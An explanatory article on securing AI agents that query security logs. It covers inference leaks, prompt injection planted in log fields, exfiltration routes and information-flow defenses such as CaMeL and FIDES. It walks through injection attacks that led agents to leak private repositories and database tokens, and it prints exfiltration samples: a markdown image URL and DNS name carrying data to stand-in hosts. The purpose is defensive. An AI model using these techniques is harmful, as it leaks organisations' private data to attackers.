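Refusals can leak information too. Suppose the agent learns that the oldest finding in the finance office is 94 days old, then asks for the oldest one without fin-0009. If the true answer is 94 again, the auditor can give it without revealing fin-0009's exact value. If the answer is lower, fin-0009 must have the 94-day-old finding, so the auditor refuses, but the agent can draw the same conclusion from the refusal.

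Kenthapadi, Mishra and Nissim (2005) proposed simulatable auditing to prevent this. The auditor decides whether to refuse a new query based on that query and the earlier queries and answers, without looking at the new answer. An attacker could make the same calculation, so they learn nothing new from a refusal. In the example, the auditor would have to refuse in both cases, which makes the system safer but less useful.

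### What agents have inferred in experiments

Today's agents can do this kind of probing themselves. In *FactGate*, Wu (2026) gave agents built on Claude models a table of ten expenses and told them they could ask only for counts. Row-level security confined them to one department, and Wu asked them to find that department's largest expense, which was 1,910. The agents asked how many expenses exceeded some amount, then halved the remaining range with each question. Twenty such questions can narrow a range by a factor of about a million. In all nine runs, the agents located the value within 19 or 20 questions, typically with an error of less than one unit.

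Wu then routed the agents' questions through a server that deducted each one from a budget for the whole task. The first count used one unit and each threshold question used two, so a budget of 12 allowed six questions. The narrowest range the agents could reach was 625 wide. The budget hardly affected nine runs of an honest task, listing large expenses. After an initial count, the agents asked for a list of every expense, which the server refused. They then narrowed the query and gave the right answer every time.

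This was a small test on one tiny table. Queries through Wu's system took 22 to 144 times as long as direct ones, and the system accepted only 22 of 40 queries that a model had written for a new set of questions. It guarantees a limit on how many facts the server releases, but not on what an agent infers from them. With the default budget of 128 units, the same halving method could recover a 64-bit number exactly. Still, the invented company could borrow the idea of one budget for each incident, shared by every agent that works on it. If the server counted only rows that those agents hadn't seen before, repeated calls would use none of the budget, but copying the whole unit would soon exhaust it.

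Wang and colleagues tried to rebuild protected data from the results of allowed queries on all six of their systems, with 25 attempts per method. When the attacker chose the queries step by step, 8 to 44% of attempts succeeded on the open-source systems, 12% on BigQuery and none on Databricks. When the attacker only stated a goal and the agent planned the queries, 20 to 40% succeeded on the open-source systems, 12% on BigQuery and 4% on Databricks. Results also varied by model. In one open-source system, attacks planned by the agent succeeded 40% of the time with DeepSeek-V3.2 but 4 to 8% with three other models. These rates depend on the agent both going along with the attack and carrying it out correctly, neither of which is needed if a script sends the same queries directly to the server.

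An agent can also reveal sensitive information by combining answers from different tools, even with no attacker involved. *Agent Tools Orchestration Leaks More* (2025) tested six models on ordinary tasks where the tools' combined results implied something sensitive. The models disclosed the sensitive information 78.7% of the time when two results were enough to imply it and 93.4% when five were needed. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) compares this to tracker attacks but doubts that the defenses against them carry over directly, because they assume statistical queries on one fixed dataset. The invented company could audit counts of machines fairly precisely but would struggle to audit counts mixed with log text and tickets.

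### Why noisy counts don't suit investigations

Differential privacy protects individual records by adding calibrated random noise to statistics. It grew out of a 2003 result by Dinur and Nissim. According to *SoK* (2026), a survey of data reconstruction attacks, they proved that an attacker can reconstruct nearly all of a database if it answers too many counting questions too accurately. *How Worrying Are Privacy Attacks Against Machine Learning?* (2025) notes that reconstruction isn't always possible, because several different databases may fit the same answers.

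Take two versions of the findings table, A and B, that differ only in whether fin-0009 is patched. The server's answers satisfy differential privacy if, for every possible set of answers and with the versions in either order:

```text
P(answers from A) ≤ e^ε × P(answers from B)
```

A smaller ε (epsilon) gives more protection, and at zero both versions of the data must produce the same answers with the same probability. To protect a count of machines, the server can add noise from a Laplace distribution with scale 1/ε. If ε is 0.5, a count is off by 2 on average. The true counts of 7 and 6 in the finance office might come back as 5 and 8, so the attacker learns little by subtracting them.

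The attacker could ask the same question many times and average out the noise. To prevent this, the server has to add up the ε of all its answers and stop answering when the sum reaches a fixed limit, or return the same noisy answer whenever someone repeats the question.

An error of 2 hardly matters in a count of how many of the company's 2,000 machines lack a patch, but it ruins an answer about one machine. If an analyst thinks there is an even chance that retail-0117 is unpatched, an answer with ε at 0.5 can raise the analyst's confidence to at most e^0.5 / (1 + e^0.5), or about 62%. More careful analysis can't raise that limit, because the noise has to hide the machine's state from everyone who receives the answer. The company could use noisy counts to compare business units, but an agent that investigates a machine needs exact answers about it.

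### Error messages, schema listings and timing

An error message can reveal a value that the server would never put in an answer. Suppose a free-form tool returns only counts, and an agent asks how many findings have a package name that equals 1 when converted to an integer. PostgreSQL can't convert the name and reports `invalid input syntax for type integer: "openssl"`. If the server forwards that message, the agent learns a package name. The server should instead return a fixed message with a reference number and record the details in a log that the agent can't read.

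Errors can also reveal that rows hidden by row-level security exist. PostgreSQL's checks for duplicate keys ignore row policies, so an agent that can add findings could try to insert one with a given ID and learn from the error that the ID is already in use. Agents that can only read the table can't do this.

Detailed error messages may show an intruder what the company isn't monitoring. Sentinel's tool for analyzing users needs certain tables, and its error message lists any that are missing. An administrator can use that list to fix the setup, but if it includes `CloudAppEvents`, an intruder learns that the company may not be recording cloud application activity in Sentinel.

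Listings of tables and settings need their own limits, because row policies hide rows but not the names of tables and columns. Splunk's MCP server has tools that list users with their roles and show saved searches and alerts. Radidiya describes new tools that return the exact condition that triggers an alert and how much longer a muted alert will stay muted. Analysts can use them to find out why they have stopped receiving an alert, but an intruder could use them to choose when to act. Most retail analysts' agents probably don't need these tools, so administrators should withhold them from the retail analyst role.

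Timing could still leak information even when every refusal message is the same. In Wu's system, the server runs a query before deciding whether to refuse it, so the delay before a refusal might reveal how much data the query touched. Wu couldn't confirm or rule this out, because random timing variation of about 2.5 milliseconds hid any effect.

An attacker can average out random variation in response times by repeating the request. If response times vary by 50 milliseconds, the average of 400 varies by only 2.5 milliseconds, which is small enough to suggest a 5-millisecond difference. At 10 calls a minute, that takes 40 minutes, so a rate limit slows this attack too. Adding random delays only increases the number of calls the attacker needs. A more reliable fix is to hold every answer until a fixed time has passed, say two seconds, and to return the same error for any query that takes longer.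 The analyst would then wait about a minute over a 30-call investigation.

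## Handling instructions that attackers write into the logs

A request can pass every check described so far and still return text that an attacker wrote for the agent to read. Suppose the analyst asks about last night's failed sign-ins on the retail machines. The server verifies the analyst, runs a fixed query and returns only retail records, but in one of them the attacker entered a username that is an instruction to the agent to disregard the other records.

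### How outsiders write into the logs

Outsiders choose the usernames, browser strings, web addresses and contents in their requests. The company logs all of this on purpose, since it may be the only trace of an attack. An attacker can therefore put instructions in the logs without having an account or persuading anyone to open a file. Pandey and Bhujang note in *Poisoning the Watchtower* (2026) that a single request can carry both the attack and the text meant to hide it.

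Failed requests are an especially effective way to plant text in logs, because programs tend to log the input that caused an error. For *When AIOps Become "AI Oops"*, Pasquini, Kornaropoulos and colleagues (2026) built a tool that sends malformed requests to every address it can find on a website. On a test social network, 120 requests left 29 records containing text that the tool had supplied.

The fields can also hold more text than their documentation suggests. LevelBlue, a security company, tested the records Windows keeps of failed sign-ins. Its consultant had read that usernames were limited to 20 characters, but the username and domain fields each accepted 120, together enough for two or three sentences. Microsoft decided that this didn't need an immediate fix.

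### Further requests and false reports

Instructions that an attacker writes into the logs can make the agent send requests the analyst didn't want. The server checks these requests like any others. The instructions can also make the agent give the analyst a false account of the logs, and the server can't prevent this.

*The Dark Side of Autonomy* (Nakajima, 2026) demonstrates both harms on a forensic agent. The agent used MCP to control Velociraptor, a tool that collects evidence from a company's computers and can run commands on them. An intruder on one machine hid instructions in the settings of a scheduled task, which the agent later read as evidence. In some demonstrations, the agent then ran the intruder's program with Velociraptor's high privileges. Giving the agent Velociraptor's investigator role prevents this, because that role can't run such commands. However, the hidden instructions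 can still make the agent report that it found no threat or blame a harmless software updater.

*NetInjectBench* (Shayoni, Shoaib and colleagues, 2026) measured how well an outside check limits unwanted actions. Three small open models read tickets, alerts and logs containing planted text that pushed them toward unsafe actions, such as unapproved network changes. Without a defense, the models chose an unsafe action in 82.5% of 240 attacks. Marking the untrusted text reduced this to 18.3%. A program that checked each change against separate approval records let no unsafe action through and still allowed every genuinely approved change. This works only if attackers can't edit the approval records.

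A false report is harder to catch, because the company has no trusted record of what the agent should have concluded.

### False authority and forged structure

Pandey and Bhujang measured how often planted text leads a model to a wrong judgment. They gave OpenAI's gpt-4o-mini, now an old model, three jobs: labeling log entries, summarizing them and recommending a response. They tested each job with four kinds of planted text and four levels of defense, for a total of 48 conditions. Each condition had 200 artificial log entries, 120 of which recorded attacks. The researchers planted text in one field of each of those 120 entries.

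Plain orders to ignore earlier instructions never got an attack labeled as harmless, probably because developers train models against that wording. Text that looked encoded failed at every task. Text that claimed authority by posing as a note from a security administrator did much better, as did text that forged the log's structure by imitating the end of the entry and adding a fake official verdict.

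| Defense | Attacks labeled harmless (false authority) | Summaries corrupted (forged structure) | Average over all attacks and jobs |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 68% | 96% | 26.6% |
| Marked fields | 15% | 75% | 17.3% |
| Marked fields and a keyword filter | 22% | 27% | 13.2% |
| Marked fields and constrained output | 33% | 38% | 11.8% |

Marked fields put each value between tags, and the prompt told the model that the values were data, not instructions. The keyword filter removed suspicious phrases before the model read them. Constrained output limited the model's answer to one of a few fixed labels or sentences.

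The averages overstate how well these defenses work because they include the two kinds of text that hardly ever worked. For false authority and forged structure alone, the attacks' average success rate fell from about 51% to about 24%. Constrained output also did worse than marked fields alone against false authority, because the model had already read the false claim before it chose a label, and a shorter list of labels couldn't undo the claim's effect.

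Most of the corrupted summaries omitted the attack, played it down or described it as needing no action, without calling it harmless. A monitoring program that searched summaries for the word "benign" would have missed nearly all of them.

An attack usually leaves several records, which makes it harder to hide. If planted text had an independent 33% chance of hiding each of five records, it would hide all five only 0.4% of the time. But Pandey and Bhujang showed the model one entry at a time, whereas an agent reads many records in the same context. Nakajima's demonstrations show that text in one record can change what the agent concludes about another.

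### Newer models and agents that call tools

Newer models mostly ignore direct instructions in a log, but plausible false claims still mislead them. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (Canale, 2026) tested Google's Gemini 4 and the smaller Gemini 3.1 flash-lite on alerts from a simulated company of 200 people. Fixed phrases instructing the model to dismiss an alert changed one of flash-lite's decisions and none of Gemini 4's.

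Canale then had another model write cover stories, for example that a suspicious program was part of an authorized repair. The attacking model received each verdict and could revise its story. Flash-lite dismissed 22% of the attacks after one attempt and 56% within eight. Gemini 4 dismissed 17% after one attempt, and three more attempts did not raise that figure. These percentages exclude attacks that the models had dismissed without any planted text, which were 19 of 46 for flash-lite and 4 of 28 for Gemini 4. An outsider who writes into a company's logs rarely sees the verdict, so the first-attempt figures are probably closer to what a real attacker would achieve.

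The models in that test only judged alerts. Pasquini and colleagues attacked agents that called tools, though with the older GPT-4o and GPT-4.1. The agents investigated faults in online services by requesting logs and measurements, and they could run commands. The planted text looked like an error message that explained the fault and suggested a fix, such as going back to a software version with a known security flaw. The agents adopted the harmful fix in 90% of 180 trials. Ten standard injection phrases, tried in the setting where the attack had worked best, never succeeded. The agents sometimes added true details of their own, such as the exact version of the web server, which made the false diagnosis more convincing.

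The analyst's wording also affects whether planted text succeeds. Nakajima ran 800 trials on four models, including Qwen3-235B and Gemini 2.5 Flash. When the analyst asked for a brief review, planted text hid the intruder's scheduled task 34 to 100% of the time, depending on the model. When the prompt required a fixed format with reasons, indicators and notable tasks, the attack succeeded 12% of the time on one model and never on the other three. Constraining the output helped much less in Pandey and Bhujang's study, perhaps because their format required only a verdict, while Nakajima's required specific evidence.

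### Filters on returned text

The company could also filter each answer before the agent reads it. In *Constrained-Action AI Remediation for SIEM/XDR via a NeMo-Guardrails Proxy*, Koutidis, Kekatos and colleagues (2026) put a filtering proxy in front of a model that analyzes alerts. One call to a language model checks the incoming text for attacks, a second analyzes the alert, and a third checks the analysis for personal data and details of the company's network.

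The model alone recognized 25.0% of 200 hostile log entries. Adding the proxy raised detection to 94.5%, and the proxy wrongly blocked one of 1,000 harmless entries. The median time per call rose from 0.31 to 14.14 seconds on the researchers' computer, so an investigation with 30 calls would take about seven minutes longer. Putting a smaller model in front to pick out suspicious text cut the median to 0.18 seconds, but detection dropped to 58.0%.

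The 94.5% is weak evidence that the proxy would catch a convincing cover story. Of the 200 hostile entries, 150 contained requests from three general jailbreak benchmarks, and the other 50 contained disguised versions of such requests. Unlike a request for help with a crime, a false ticket number doesn't stand out in a sign-in record. Microsoft's Prompt Shields and Meta's Prompt Guard 2 missed Pasquini and colleagues' false diagnoses every time, and DataSentinel, a research filter, missed them 85% of the time.

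A filter can help an attacker. When Koutidis and colleagues' proxy blocks a message, it returns a standard refusal and the main model never sees the text. An intruder could therefore add an obvious injection to a record to keep the agent from reading that record. *Poisoning the SOC*, Seymour's poster at the DEF CON 34 security conference, lists this kind of denial of analysis among the practical effects of injected log text.

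A server that filters out records containing instructions to the agent should report the number withheld to the agent and alert an analyst. Ordinary visitors have little reason to write instructions to a language model in the username box, so such text is good evidence of an attack.

### Closed lists of actions

Some companies also let the agent respond to what it finds. Koutidis and colleagues' system allows only six kinds of action: blocking an address, ending a process, quarantining a file, deleting a file, disabling a user account and running a script defined in the system's own templates. The model picks an action and supplies a target, such as an address. Ordinary code then checks the target's format, inserts the target into a prewritten command and scans the result for forbidden programs and characters. The model never writes commands itself, so planted text can't make it write a malicious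 one.

In a live test with 54 alerts from three simulated attacks, the model proposed 41 actions:

- For repeated password guessing, it proposed blocking the attacker's address 36 times, correctly each time.
- For a malicious program, it proposed ending a process but took the target from the wrong field. The format check would have rejected this.
- For the misuse of a valid account, it proposed blocking an address four times and never proposed disabling the account.

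All 41 actions needed a person's approval, and the system carried out none of them.

The list limits the third mistake only by restricting the agent to a permitted action, in this case blocking an address. The stolen account would have kept working. An attacker could also steer the agent toward a harmful choice from the list. In LevelBlue's demonstration, text planted in a failed sign-in made a model report a false source address and a false workstation name. An agent that relied on such a report might propose blocking the false address. The format check accepts any real address, even one that belongs to the company's payment service.

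The invented company could reduce this risk by having the agent name a record instead of an address. The server would then read the address from that record's address field. The company could also list machines that the agent may never block, and require approval for actions that are hard to undo, such as deleting a file.

Dismissing an alert is also an action, and the company can restrict it in the same way. In Canale's full system, ordinary code decides which alerts the model may dismiss and sends those with a high risk score straight to analysts. Of the 127 attacks that the system detected, 102 reached analysts regardless of what the model concluded. Gemini 4 hid none of the other 25, though it hid four attacks in a later set of simulations. Canale also tested seven attacks with cover stories. All seven still reached analysts, because each had also raised an alert that the attacker couldn't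 write into. Seven is a small sample, but this approach doesn't depend on the model recognizing the deception.

### Omitting and shortening fields

Action lists limit what the agent can do after it has read planted text. The server can also keep much of that text from reaching the agent. For example, the agent doesn't need usernames to find out which retail machines had more than 20 failed sign-ins last night, so a fixed query can leave out the username column. This is much harder with free-form queries, because the agent can combine a username with another column and rename the result.

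Shortening a field leaves less room for planted text while keeping some of the evidence. If the server cut usernames and domains to 20 characters each, the record that LevelBlue tested would have room for 40 characters of planted text instead of 240. But a false claim of authority can be very short, so it might still fit. Shortening can also remove the evidence of an attack, such as a database command at the end of a long web address.

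Pasquini and colleagues replaced attacker-written values with stable placeholders, much like the codes a server can use to hide personal data. To identify the fields that needed placeholders, they sent a unique string through every input they could find and searched the logs for it. With the placeholders, none of their attacks succeeded. They also ran 12 fault-finding tasks three times each without any attack, and the agent solved 17 of 36 runs with placeholders and 18 of 36 without them.

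Placeholders would probably remove more useful information in security work. A visitor's text rarely helps to explain a wrong port setting, but it is often the main evidence of an attack. If the server replaced every web address with a placeholder, the agent couldn't tell an attempted database attack from a mistyped link. Placeholders also protect only the fields that the search found, so the company has to repeat the search whenever a program changes what it logs.

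### Labeling the origin of each field

When the agent needs the text itself, the server can state where each value came from:

```json
{
  "event": "failed_sign_in",
  "source_address": {"value": "203.0.113.7", "origin": "system"},
  "username": {"value": "m.okafor", "origin": "visitor"}
}
```

Labeling log text removes no evidence that the investigator might need, but planted text can imitate the labels. A JSON parser can determine exactly where a value ends because any quotation marks inside it are escaped, whereas a language model has to infer this. Choi, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents*, planted text that looked like extra fields or records, such as a comment with a false author. Six models, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.5, accepted the false data 31 to 43% of the time when it arrived in JSON.

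False data planted in the logs contains no instructions, so training a model to ignore instructions doesn't help much. When Choi and colleagues tested whole agents built on GPT-5.2, planted instructions succeeded 0.2% of the time and planted data succeeded 49.1% of the time. Newer models may do better, but Canale's results with cover stories suggest that false data is still a problem.

The server can make its labels harder to forge by adding a random suffix to the field names in each answer, so that `origin` might become `origin_f7x9k2`. The agent's prompt then has to tell the model to trust only fields with that suffix. In Choi and colleagues' tests of single answers in JSON, this cut the attacks' success rate to 3% or less. The models' accuracy on ordinary questions fell by up to 7 percentage points, though the drop was smaller for most models.

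In tests of whole agents, attacks still succeeded 28.7% of the time. Most of the successful attacks added a false entry to a list, and the agent included it in a total without checking the suffix. The server can prevent this by computing totals itself.

Choi and colleagues also tried removing quotation marks, brackets and similar characters from untrusted fields. This worked about as well in JSON, but accuracy fell from 81–85% to 68–72% because web addresses and file paths contain those characters too. In a security log, these characters may also be part of the attack the analyst is trying to understand.

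### Returning typed values and counts

*From Investigation Failures to Reliable SOC Agents* describes a triage system in which only one component contacts the SIEM, and that component contains no language model. *From Investigation Failures to Reliable SOC Agents* (2026) has this component run the agent's requests and turn each reply into a typed entry before any model reads it. A mediating server can do the same. Instead of 212 failed sign-ins, it might return:

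```json
{
  "event": "failed_sign_in",
  "count": 212,
  "source_address": "203.0.113.7",
  "usernames_tried": 41,
  "usernames_that_exist": 3,
  "longest_username": 118,
  "longest_username_record": 88213
}
```

The agent can see that one address tried many accounts and that one username was suspiciously long. None of these values can contain a sentence, provided the server checks that the address is valid. A field of type "text" would not give this protection. Counts can also expose the agent to text, because a count for each browser string includes the string itself. The server should therefore count known browsers by name and group everything else under "other".

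The attacker can no longer tell the agent how to interpret the numbers, but can still influence them, for example by making thousands of pointless sign-in attempts to hide the important ones.

The investigator can't see anything that the server's developers didn't think to measure. To report that a web request contained a database attack, the server needs a rule that recognizes one, and rules are poor at detecting attacks that their writers didn't know about. In Canale's simulation, rules detected 85% of attacks of the types they had been tuned on, but only 22% of attacks of types added later. An agent that reads the raw request might notice an attack that no rule covers.

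### Keeping raw text for people

The answer above gives the number of record 88213 but not its text. An analyst who needs the text can open the record in the SIEM, or the server can show it in a window that the model can't read. Pasquini and colleagues' placeholders also leave the original logs available to people.

Withholding records keeps all the evidence but slows the work. An analyst may need a minute to open and read each one, so 50 would take most of an hour. An agent that sorts alerts overnight has to leave withheld records until morning or wake someone up.

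Human approval protects much less when the person sees only the agent's account of a record. Choi and colleagues tricked coding agents with comments that appeared to come from a project's maintainer. The agents asked for permission before running the planted command, but they presented it as the maintainer's recommendation. The analyst therefore has to see the original record, with the fields that outsiders wrote clearly marked.

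The analyst may want a model to explain the text, for instance when it contains an unfamiliar command. If they paste it into the agent's chat, the planted text is back in the context of a model that can call tools. The server could instead send the record to a separate model that has no tools and show its explanation only to the analyst. The planted text then couldn't trigger further requests, though it could still make the explanation wrong.

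## Closing the routes by which retrieved data can leave

A model without tools can't send anything anywhere. The analyst's main agent, however, often has tools from several servers. Suppose it can use both the findings server and the company's email server, and an intruder has planted a username that tells it to mail out a list of unpatched machines. If the agent complies, it makes three calls:

| Call | Server | Why the server allows it |
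|---|---|---|
| Read last night's failed sign-ins | Findings | The records belong to the retail unit |
| List internet-facing machines with critical flaws | Findings | The analyst may see all 40 machines |
| Send the list to an outside address | Email | The analyst may send email |

The intruder gets the list even though both servers enforce their own rules perfectly. The data moves from one server to the other through the model's context. The findings server cannot detect the email because it receives only the calls addressed to it.

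### Three conditions for theft

Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for three conditions that together let an attacker steal data through an agent: the agent can access private data, it reads content that an attacker may have written, and it can communicate with outside systems.

Security logs supply the first two conditions at once. A table of failed sign-ins, for example, contains both private data and hostile text. In other systems, the two often come from different places, such as a customer database and a public web page, so a company can let an agent read one and not the other. Returning counts instead of text from the logs helps, but an investigation usually needs some of the text, so the company has to concentrate on closing the routes by which data can leave.

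There are many ways out. Willison's examples include a tool that makes web requests, an image that the host loads and a link that the user clicks. The image needs no tool call at all. If the host displays images in its chat window, the agent can write this in its reply:

```text
![chart](https://img.example.net/c.png?d=retail-0117:openssl:94)
```

The analyst's computer then requests the image, and the attacker reads the data in the web server's log. An incident's 90 rows, at about 20 characters each, total 1,800 characters, which can fit in one web address.

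Willison lists dozens of such flaws in commercial products since 2023. The vendors fixed nearly all of them quickly, usually by blocking the route by which data could leave. But MCP encourages users to combine tools from different sources, and no single vendor controls the combination.

### The GitHub and Supabase demonstrations

One server can meet all three conditions by itself. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) demonstrates this with the official MCP server for GitHub, a site where developers store code in repositories:

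1. The attacker posts a bug report containing instructions for an agent in a user's public repository, where anyone may post.
2. The user asks an agent running Claude 4 Opus to look at the repository's open reports.
3. The agent reads the planted instructions and follows them by reading the user's private repositories.
4. It proposes a change to the public repository that contains what it read, including the user's salary and plans to move abroad.

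The host asks users to confirm each call by default, but Invariant Labs notes that many choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

The second demonstration, by General Analysis, concerned Supabase, a company that provides PostgreSQL databases. Willison (2025), in *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database*, explains how it worked:

1. The attacker files a support ticket that tells the agent to read a table of access tokens and add its contents to the ticket.
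2. A developer asks a coding agent to list the latest tickets.
3. The agent reads the tokens, which it can do because its database account bypasses row-level security.
4. It writes them into the ticket as a new message, which the attacker can read.

Here the data left through an ordinary database write. Supabase's documentation already recommended a read-only mode, which would have prevented this write. Supabase replied in *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) that no customer had reported a leak through MCP. It had tried putting warnings around query results and using models to detect dangerous content, but these measures only reduced the risk. It now advises customers never to connect agents to production data.

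The proposed fixes affect different conditions:

| Fix | Condition it removes |
|---|---|
| Supabase: read-only mode | The way out through the database |
| Supabase: test data only | Private data |
| Supabase: warnings around results | None, though the model is less likely to obey planted text |
| GitHub: one repository per session | Private data, in sessions that read a public repository |
| Both: a person approves each call | None, though the person can block the last step |

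Read-only mode closes only one route. If the developer's agent also had an email tool, it could email the tokens. Test data is no use to a security team, which has to investigate real logs. The GitHub rule is the most interesting for the invented company because it depends on what the agent has already done. Invariant Labs argues that GitHub can't solve the problem by patching its server, and wants a layer outside the server to enforce the rule. Invariant Labs sells software that does this, but its argument is sound because a patched GitHub server still couldn't monitor the agent's other tools.

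A findings server with any write tool needs the same scrutiny. If the agent can add comments to a finding and an outside contractor can read them, retrieved data can leave through those comments.

### Removing, supervising or blocking outbound calls

The simplest remedy is to give the agent no outbound tools. It can use only the findings server, and the host shows its replies as plain text without images or links. The analyst sends any emails. To check whether an address is known to be malicious, the findings server can search a downloaded list, so the agent doesn't have to ask an outside service. An agent that works overnight still needs a way to wake someone up, but this can be a function that takes only an incident number and pages the analyst on call. Because the function has no text field, it can carry very little stolen data.

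If the agent needs more tools than that, the company can route all its tool calls through a gateway, a program between the host and every server. The gateway sees the whole sequence and can apply a rule such as this one:

```text
if an agent on this incident has received data from the findings server:
    allow email only to addresses inside the company
    block web requests
    block comments that outsiders can read
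```

The rule depends on what the agent has read because checking the outgoing text is unreliable. An agent can encode a list of machines so that no machine name appears in it. Because MCP is stateless, the gateway also has to keep its own history, which it should file under the verified user and incident. If the history were reset with each conversation, an agent could save data in a note during one and email it during the next.

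A gateway can check only the traffic that passes through it. Many hosts can send data around it through built-in tools, such as a browser or a command line, or by loading images, which requires no tool call. A script that has replaced the host can also contact the email server directly if the host holds an email token. The gateway should therefore keep the tokens for the other servers and never give them to the host.

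A firewall outside the agent's computer can close some of these gaps by allowing connections only to the gateway, the sign-in service and the model's provider. This blocks the image in the example above and command-line connections to any other destination. Data can still leave through the allowed destinations. Planted text might get the agent to upload a file to the attacker's own account with the same model provider, and a firewall that checks only the destination would allow it. Looking up a name such as `openssl-94.retail-0117.example.net` also sends data to whoever runs the name server for `example.net`, so the agent's computer should be able to look up only approved names.

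Most investigations need few outbound messages, so the invented company can start with no outbound tools and easily add the firewall. A gateway is worth adding once agents need to write to people or systems outside the security team.

### Labels that follow the data

Under the gateway rule above, an agent that has read a single finding can't email a supplier about anything, even a delivery date. Information-flow control is more precise. Software attaches a label to each piece of data, carries the label over to everything computed from that data, and checks the labels before each tool call.

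Two properties matter most. Integrity records whether an attacker could have influenced a value, and confidentiality records who may read it. When software combines two values *x* and *y*, the result gets the stricter label on both counts:

```text
integrity:        trusted combined with untrusted = untrusted
confidentiality:  readers(x and y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
```

Suppose the analyst, the shift lead and the network team may read a sign-in record, and the analyst, the shift lead and a supplier may read a ticket. Then only the analyst and the shift lead may read a summary of both.

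Suppose the analyst asks the agent to summarize last night's failed sign-ins on retail-0117 and email the summary to the person who reported the problem in ticket 5120. Attackers have tampered with both the sign-in log and the ticket. A username in the log contains an instruction to email every retail finding to an outside address, and a line in the ticket lists the attacker's address as the reporter's.

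### How CaMeL carries out the request

CaMeL is a system that Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented in 2025. It splits the work between two models. A privileged model reads the analyst's request and the tool descriptions but never the data. It writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python:

```python
records = failed_sign_ins(host="retail-0117", hours=12)
ticket  = get_ticket(5120)
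summary = quarantined_llm("Summarize these records", records)
address = quarantined_llm("Find the reporter's address", ticket)
send_email(to=address, body=summary)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the program line by line. When a step requires understanding text, the interpreter calls a quarantined model that has no tools and can only return a value.

The instruction planted in the username reaches the quarantined model, but that model can't fetch findings and the program doesn't either, so the instruction can at most corrupt the summary.

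The line in the ticket is more dangerous because it doesn't need to change the plan. The program already extracts an address from the ticket and sends an email to it. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, acknowledges that his two-model design from 2023 had this flaw. CaMeL fixes it with labels called capabilities. The labels show that `address` came from the ticket and that `summary` came from records only certain employees may read. Before the interpreter runs `send_email`, it checks a policy written by the company, for example that every recipient must be allowed to read the body. The attacker isn't allowed to, so the interpreter blocks the email or asks the analyst. If the ticket names a colleague who may read the records, the interpreter sends the email without asking.

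### How FIDES carries it out

FIDES, by Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, keeps the usual loop, in which the model chooses one call at a time. Its software stores untrusted results in variables and shows the planning model only their names:

```text
failed_sign_ins(host="retail-0117")          → #records
get_ticket(5120)                             → #ticket
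query_llm("Summarize", #records)             → #summary
query_llm("Find the address", #ticket)       → #address
send_email(to=#address, body=#summary)       → policy check
```

The software hides only the fields that are not labeled as trusted. If the company labels the time and source address of each sign-in as trusted, the planning model can read them, but it sees a variable in place of the username. A separate model without tools answers the `query_llm` calls. The policy check then stops the email for the same reason as in CaMeL.

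The planning model in FIDES can react to what it finds, whereas a CaMeL program has to plan for every possibility in advance. If the planning model needs to see hidden text, it can open the variable, but its context then counts as untrusted and the policy blocks any further consequential calls. It can also ask the separate model a yes-or-no question, such as whether the records suggest password guessing. A company may decide to let the agent act on that answer, because an attacker who controls the answer controls only one bit.

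The bits revealed by yes-or-no answers add up over many questions. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) tested a version of FIDES that let the planner read such answers about the screen. It warns that the planner could eventually learn everything on the screen by repeating these questions, so the researchers capped the number of calls.

The findings server can supply the labels for either system, since it can identify which fields visitors wrote and who may see each row. Ordinary code enforces these labels, so the model can't bypass them.

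### Results and costs

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 office tasks in four simulated settings, using the now old GPT-4o. Without policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks on, none succeeded against either. The checks therefore provided the guarantee, and hiding text in variables mainly helped the agent to finish more of its work despite them, as the share of tasks completed without an attack shows:

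| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% |
| Ordinary agent with checks | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% |
| FIDES with checks | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% |

On average, FIDES completed 8 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary agent with checks. With OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, it completed 16 points more. Many of the failures were intentional. For example, several banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy forbids.

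CaMeL's policies similarly reduce the number of tasks it completes. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with newer models. The policies blocked every attack in the runs that finished, but CaMeL completed only 37.5% of tasks, about half as many as with the policies off. The paper also found that in 97 of the 144 task-attack pairs, the attack needed a tool call that the task's program would normally never contain. Planning before reading is enough to stop most of these attacks, but it failed in two runs without policies, where the planner had written a program that followed any instructions it found in a file.

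In a November 2026 test reported in *The Devil is in the Context* (2026), attacks succeeded 17.5% of the time without a defense, 7.5% with a filter called PromptArmor and 2.5% with CaMeL. The agent completed 90% of its tasks with PromptArmor and 27.5% with CaMeL. PromptArmor is the sensible choice for data of little value. But Nasr and colleagues' results suggest that attacks on PromptArmor would succeed more often if the attacker adapted to it, while CaMeL's protection doesn't depend on recognizing hostile text.

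CaMeL also used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens for the median AgentDojo task, according to *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025).

CaMeL reduces usefulness less with better models. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) tested CaMeL without policies on 112 industrial maintenance tasks. CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures occurred because the agent learned something midway that its program hadn't provided for. This happens often in investigations, so CaMeL probably suits routine reports better than threat hunting.

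### Leaks, blocked work and later designs

CaMeL's labels can miss information that a program reveals through the path it takes. Garby and colleagues give an example that works like this one, in which `unpatched` is secret:

```python
a = True
b = True
if unpatched: a = False    # a now carries the secret label
if a:         b = False    # skipped, so b keeps its public label
if b:         send_email("outsider@example.net", "unpatched")
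```

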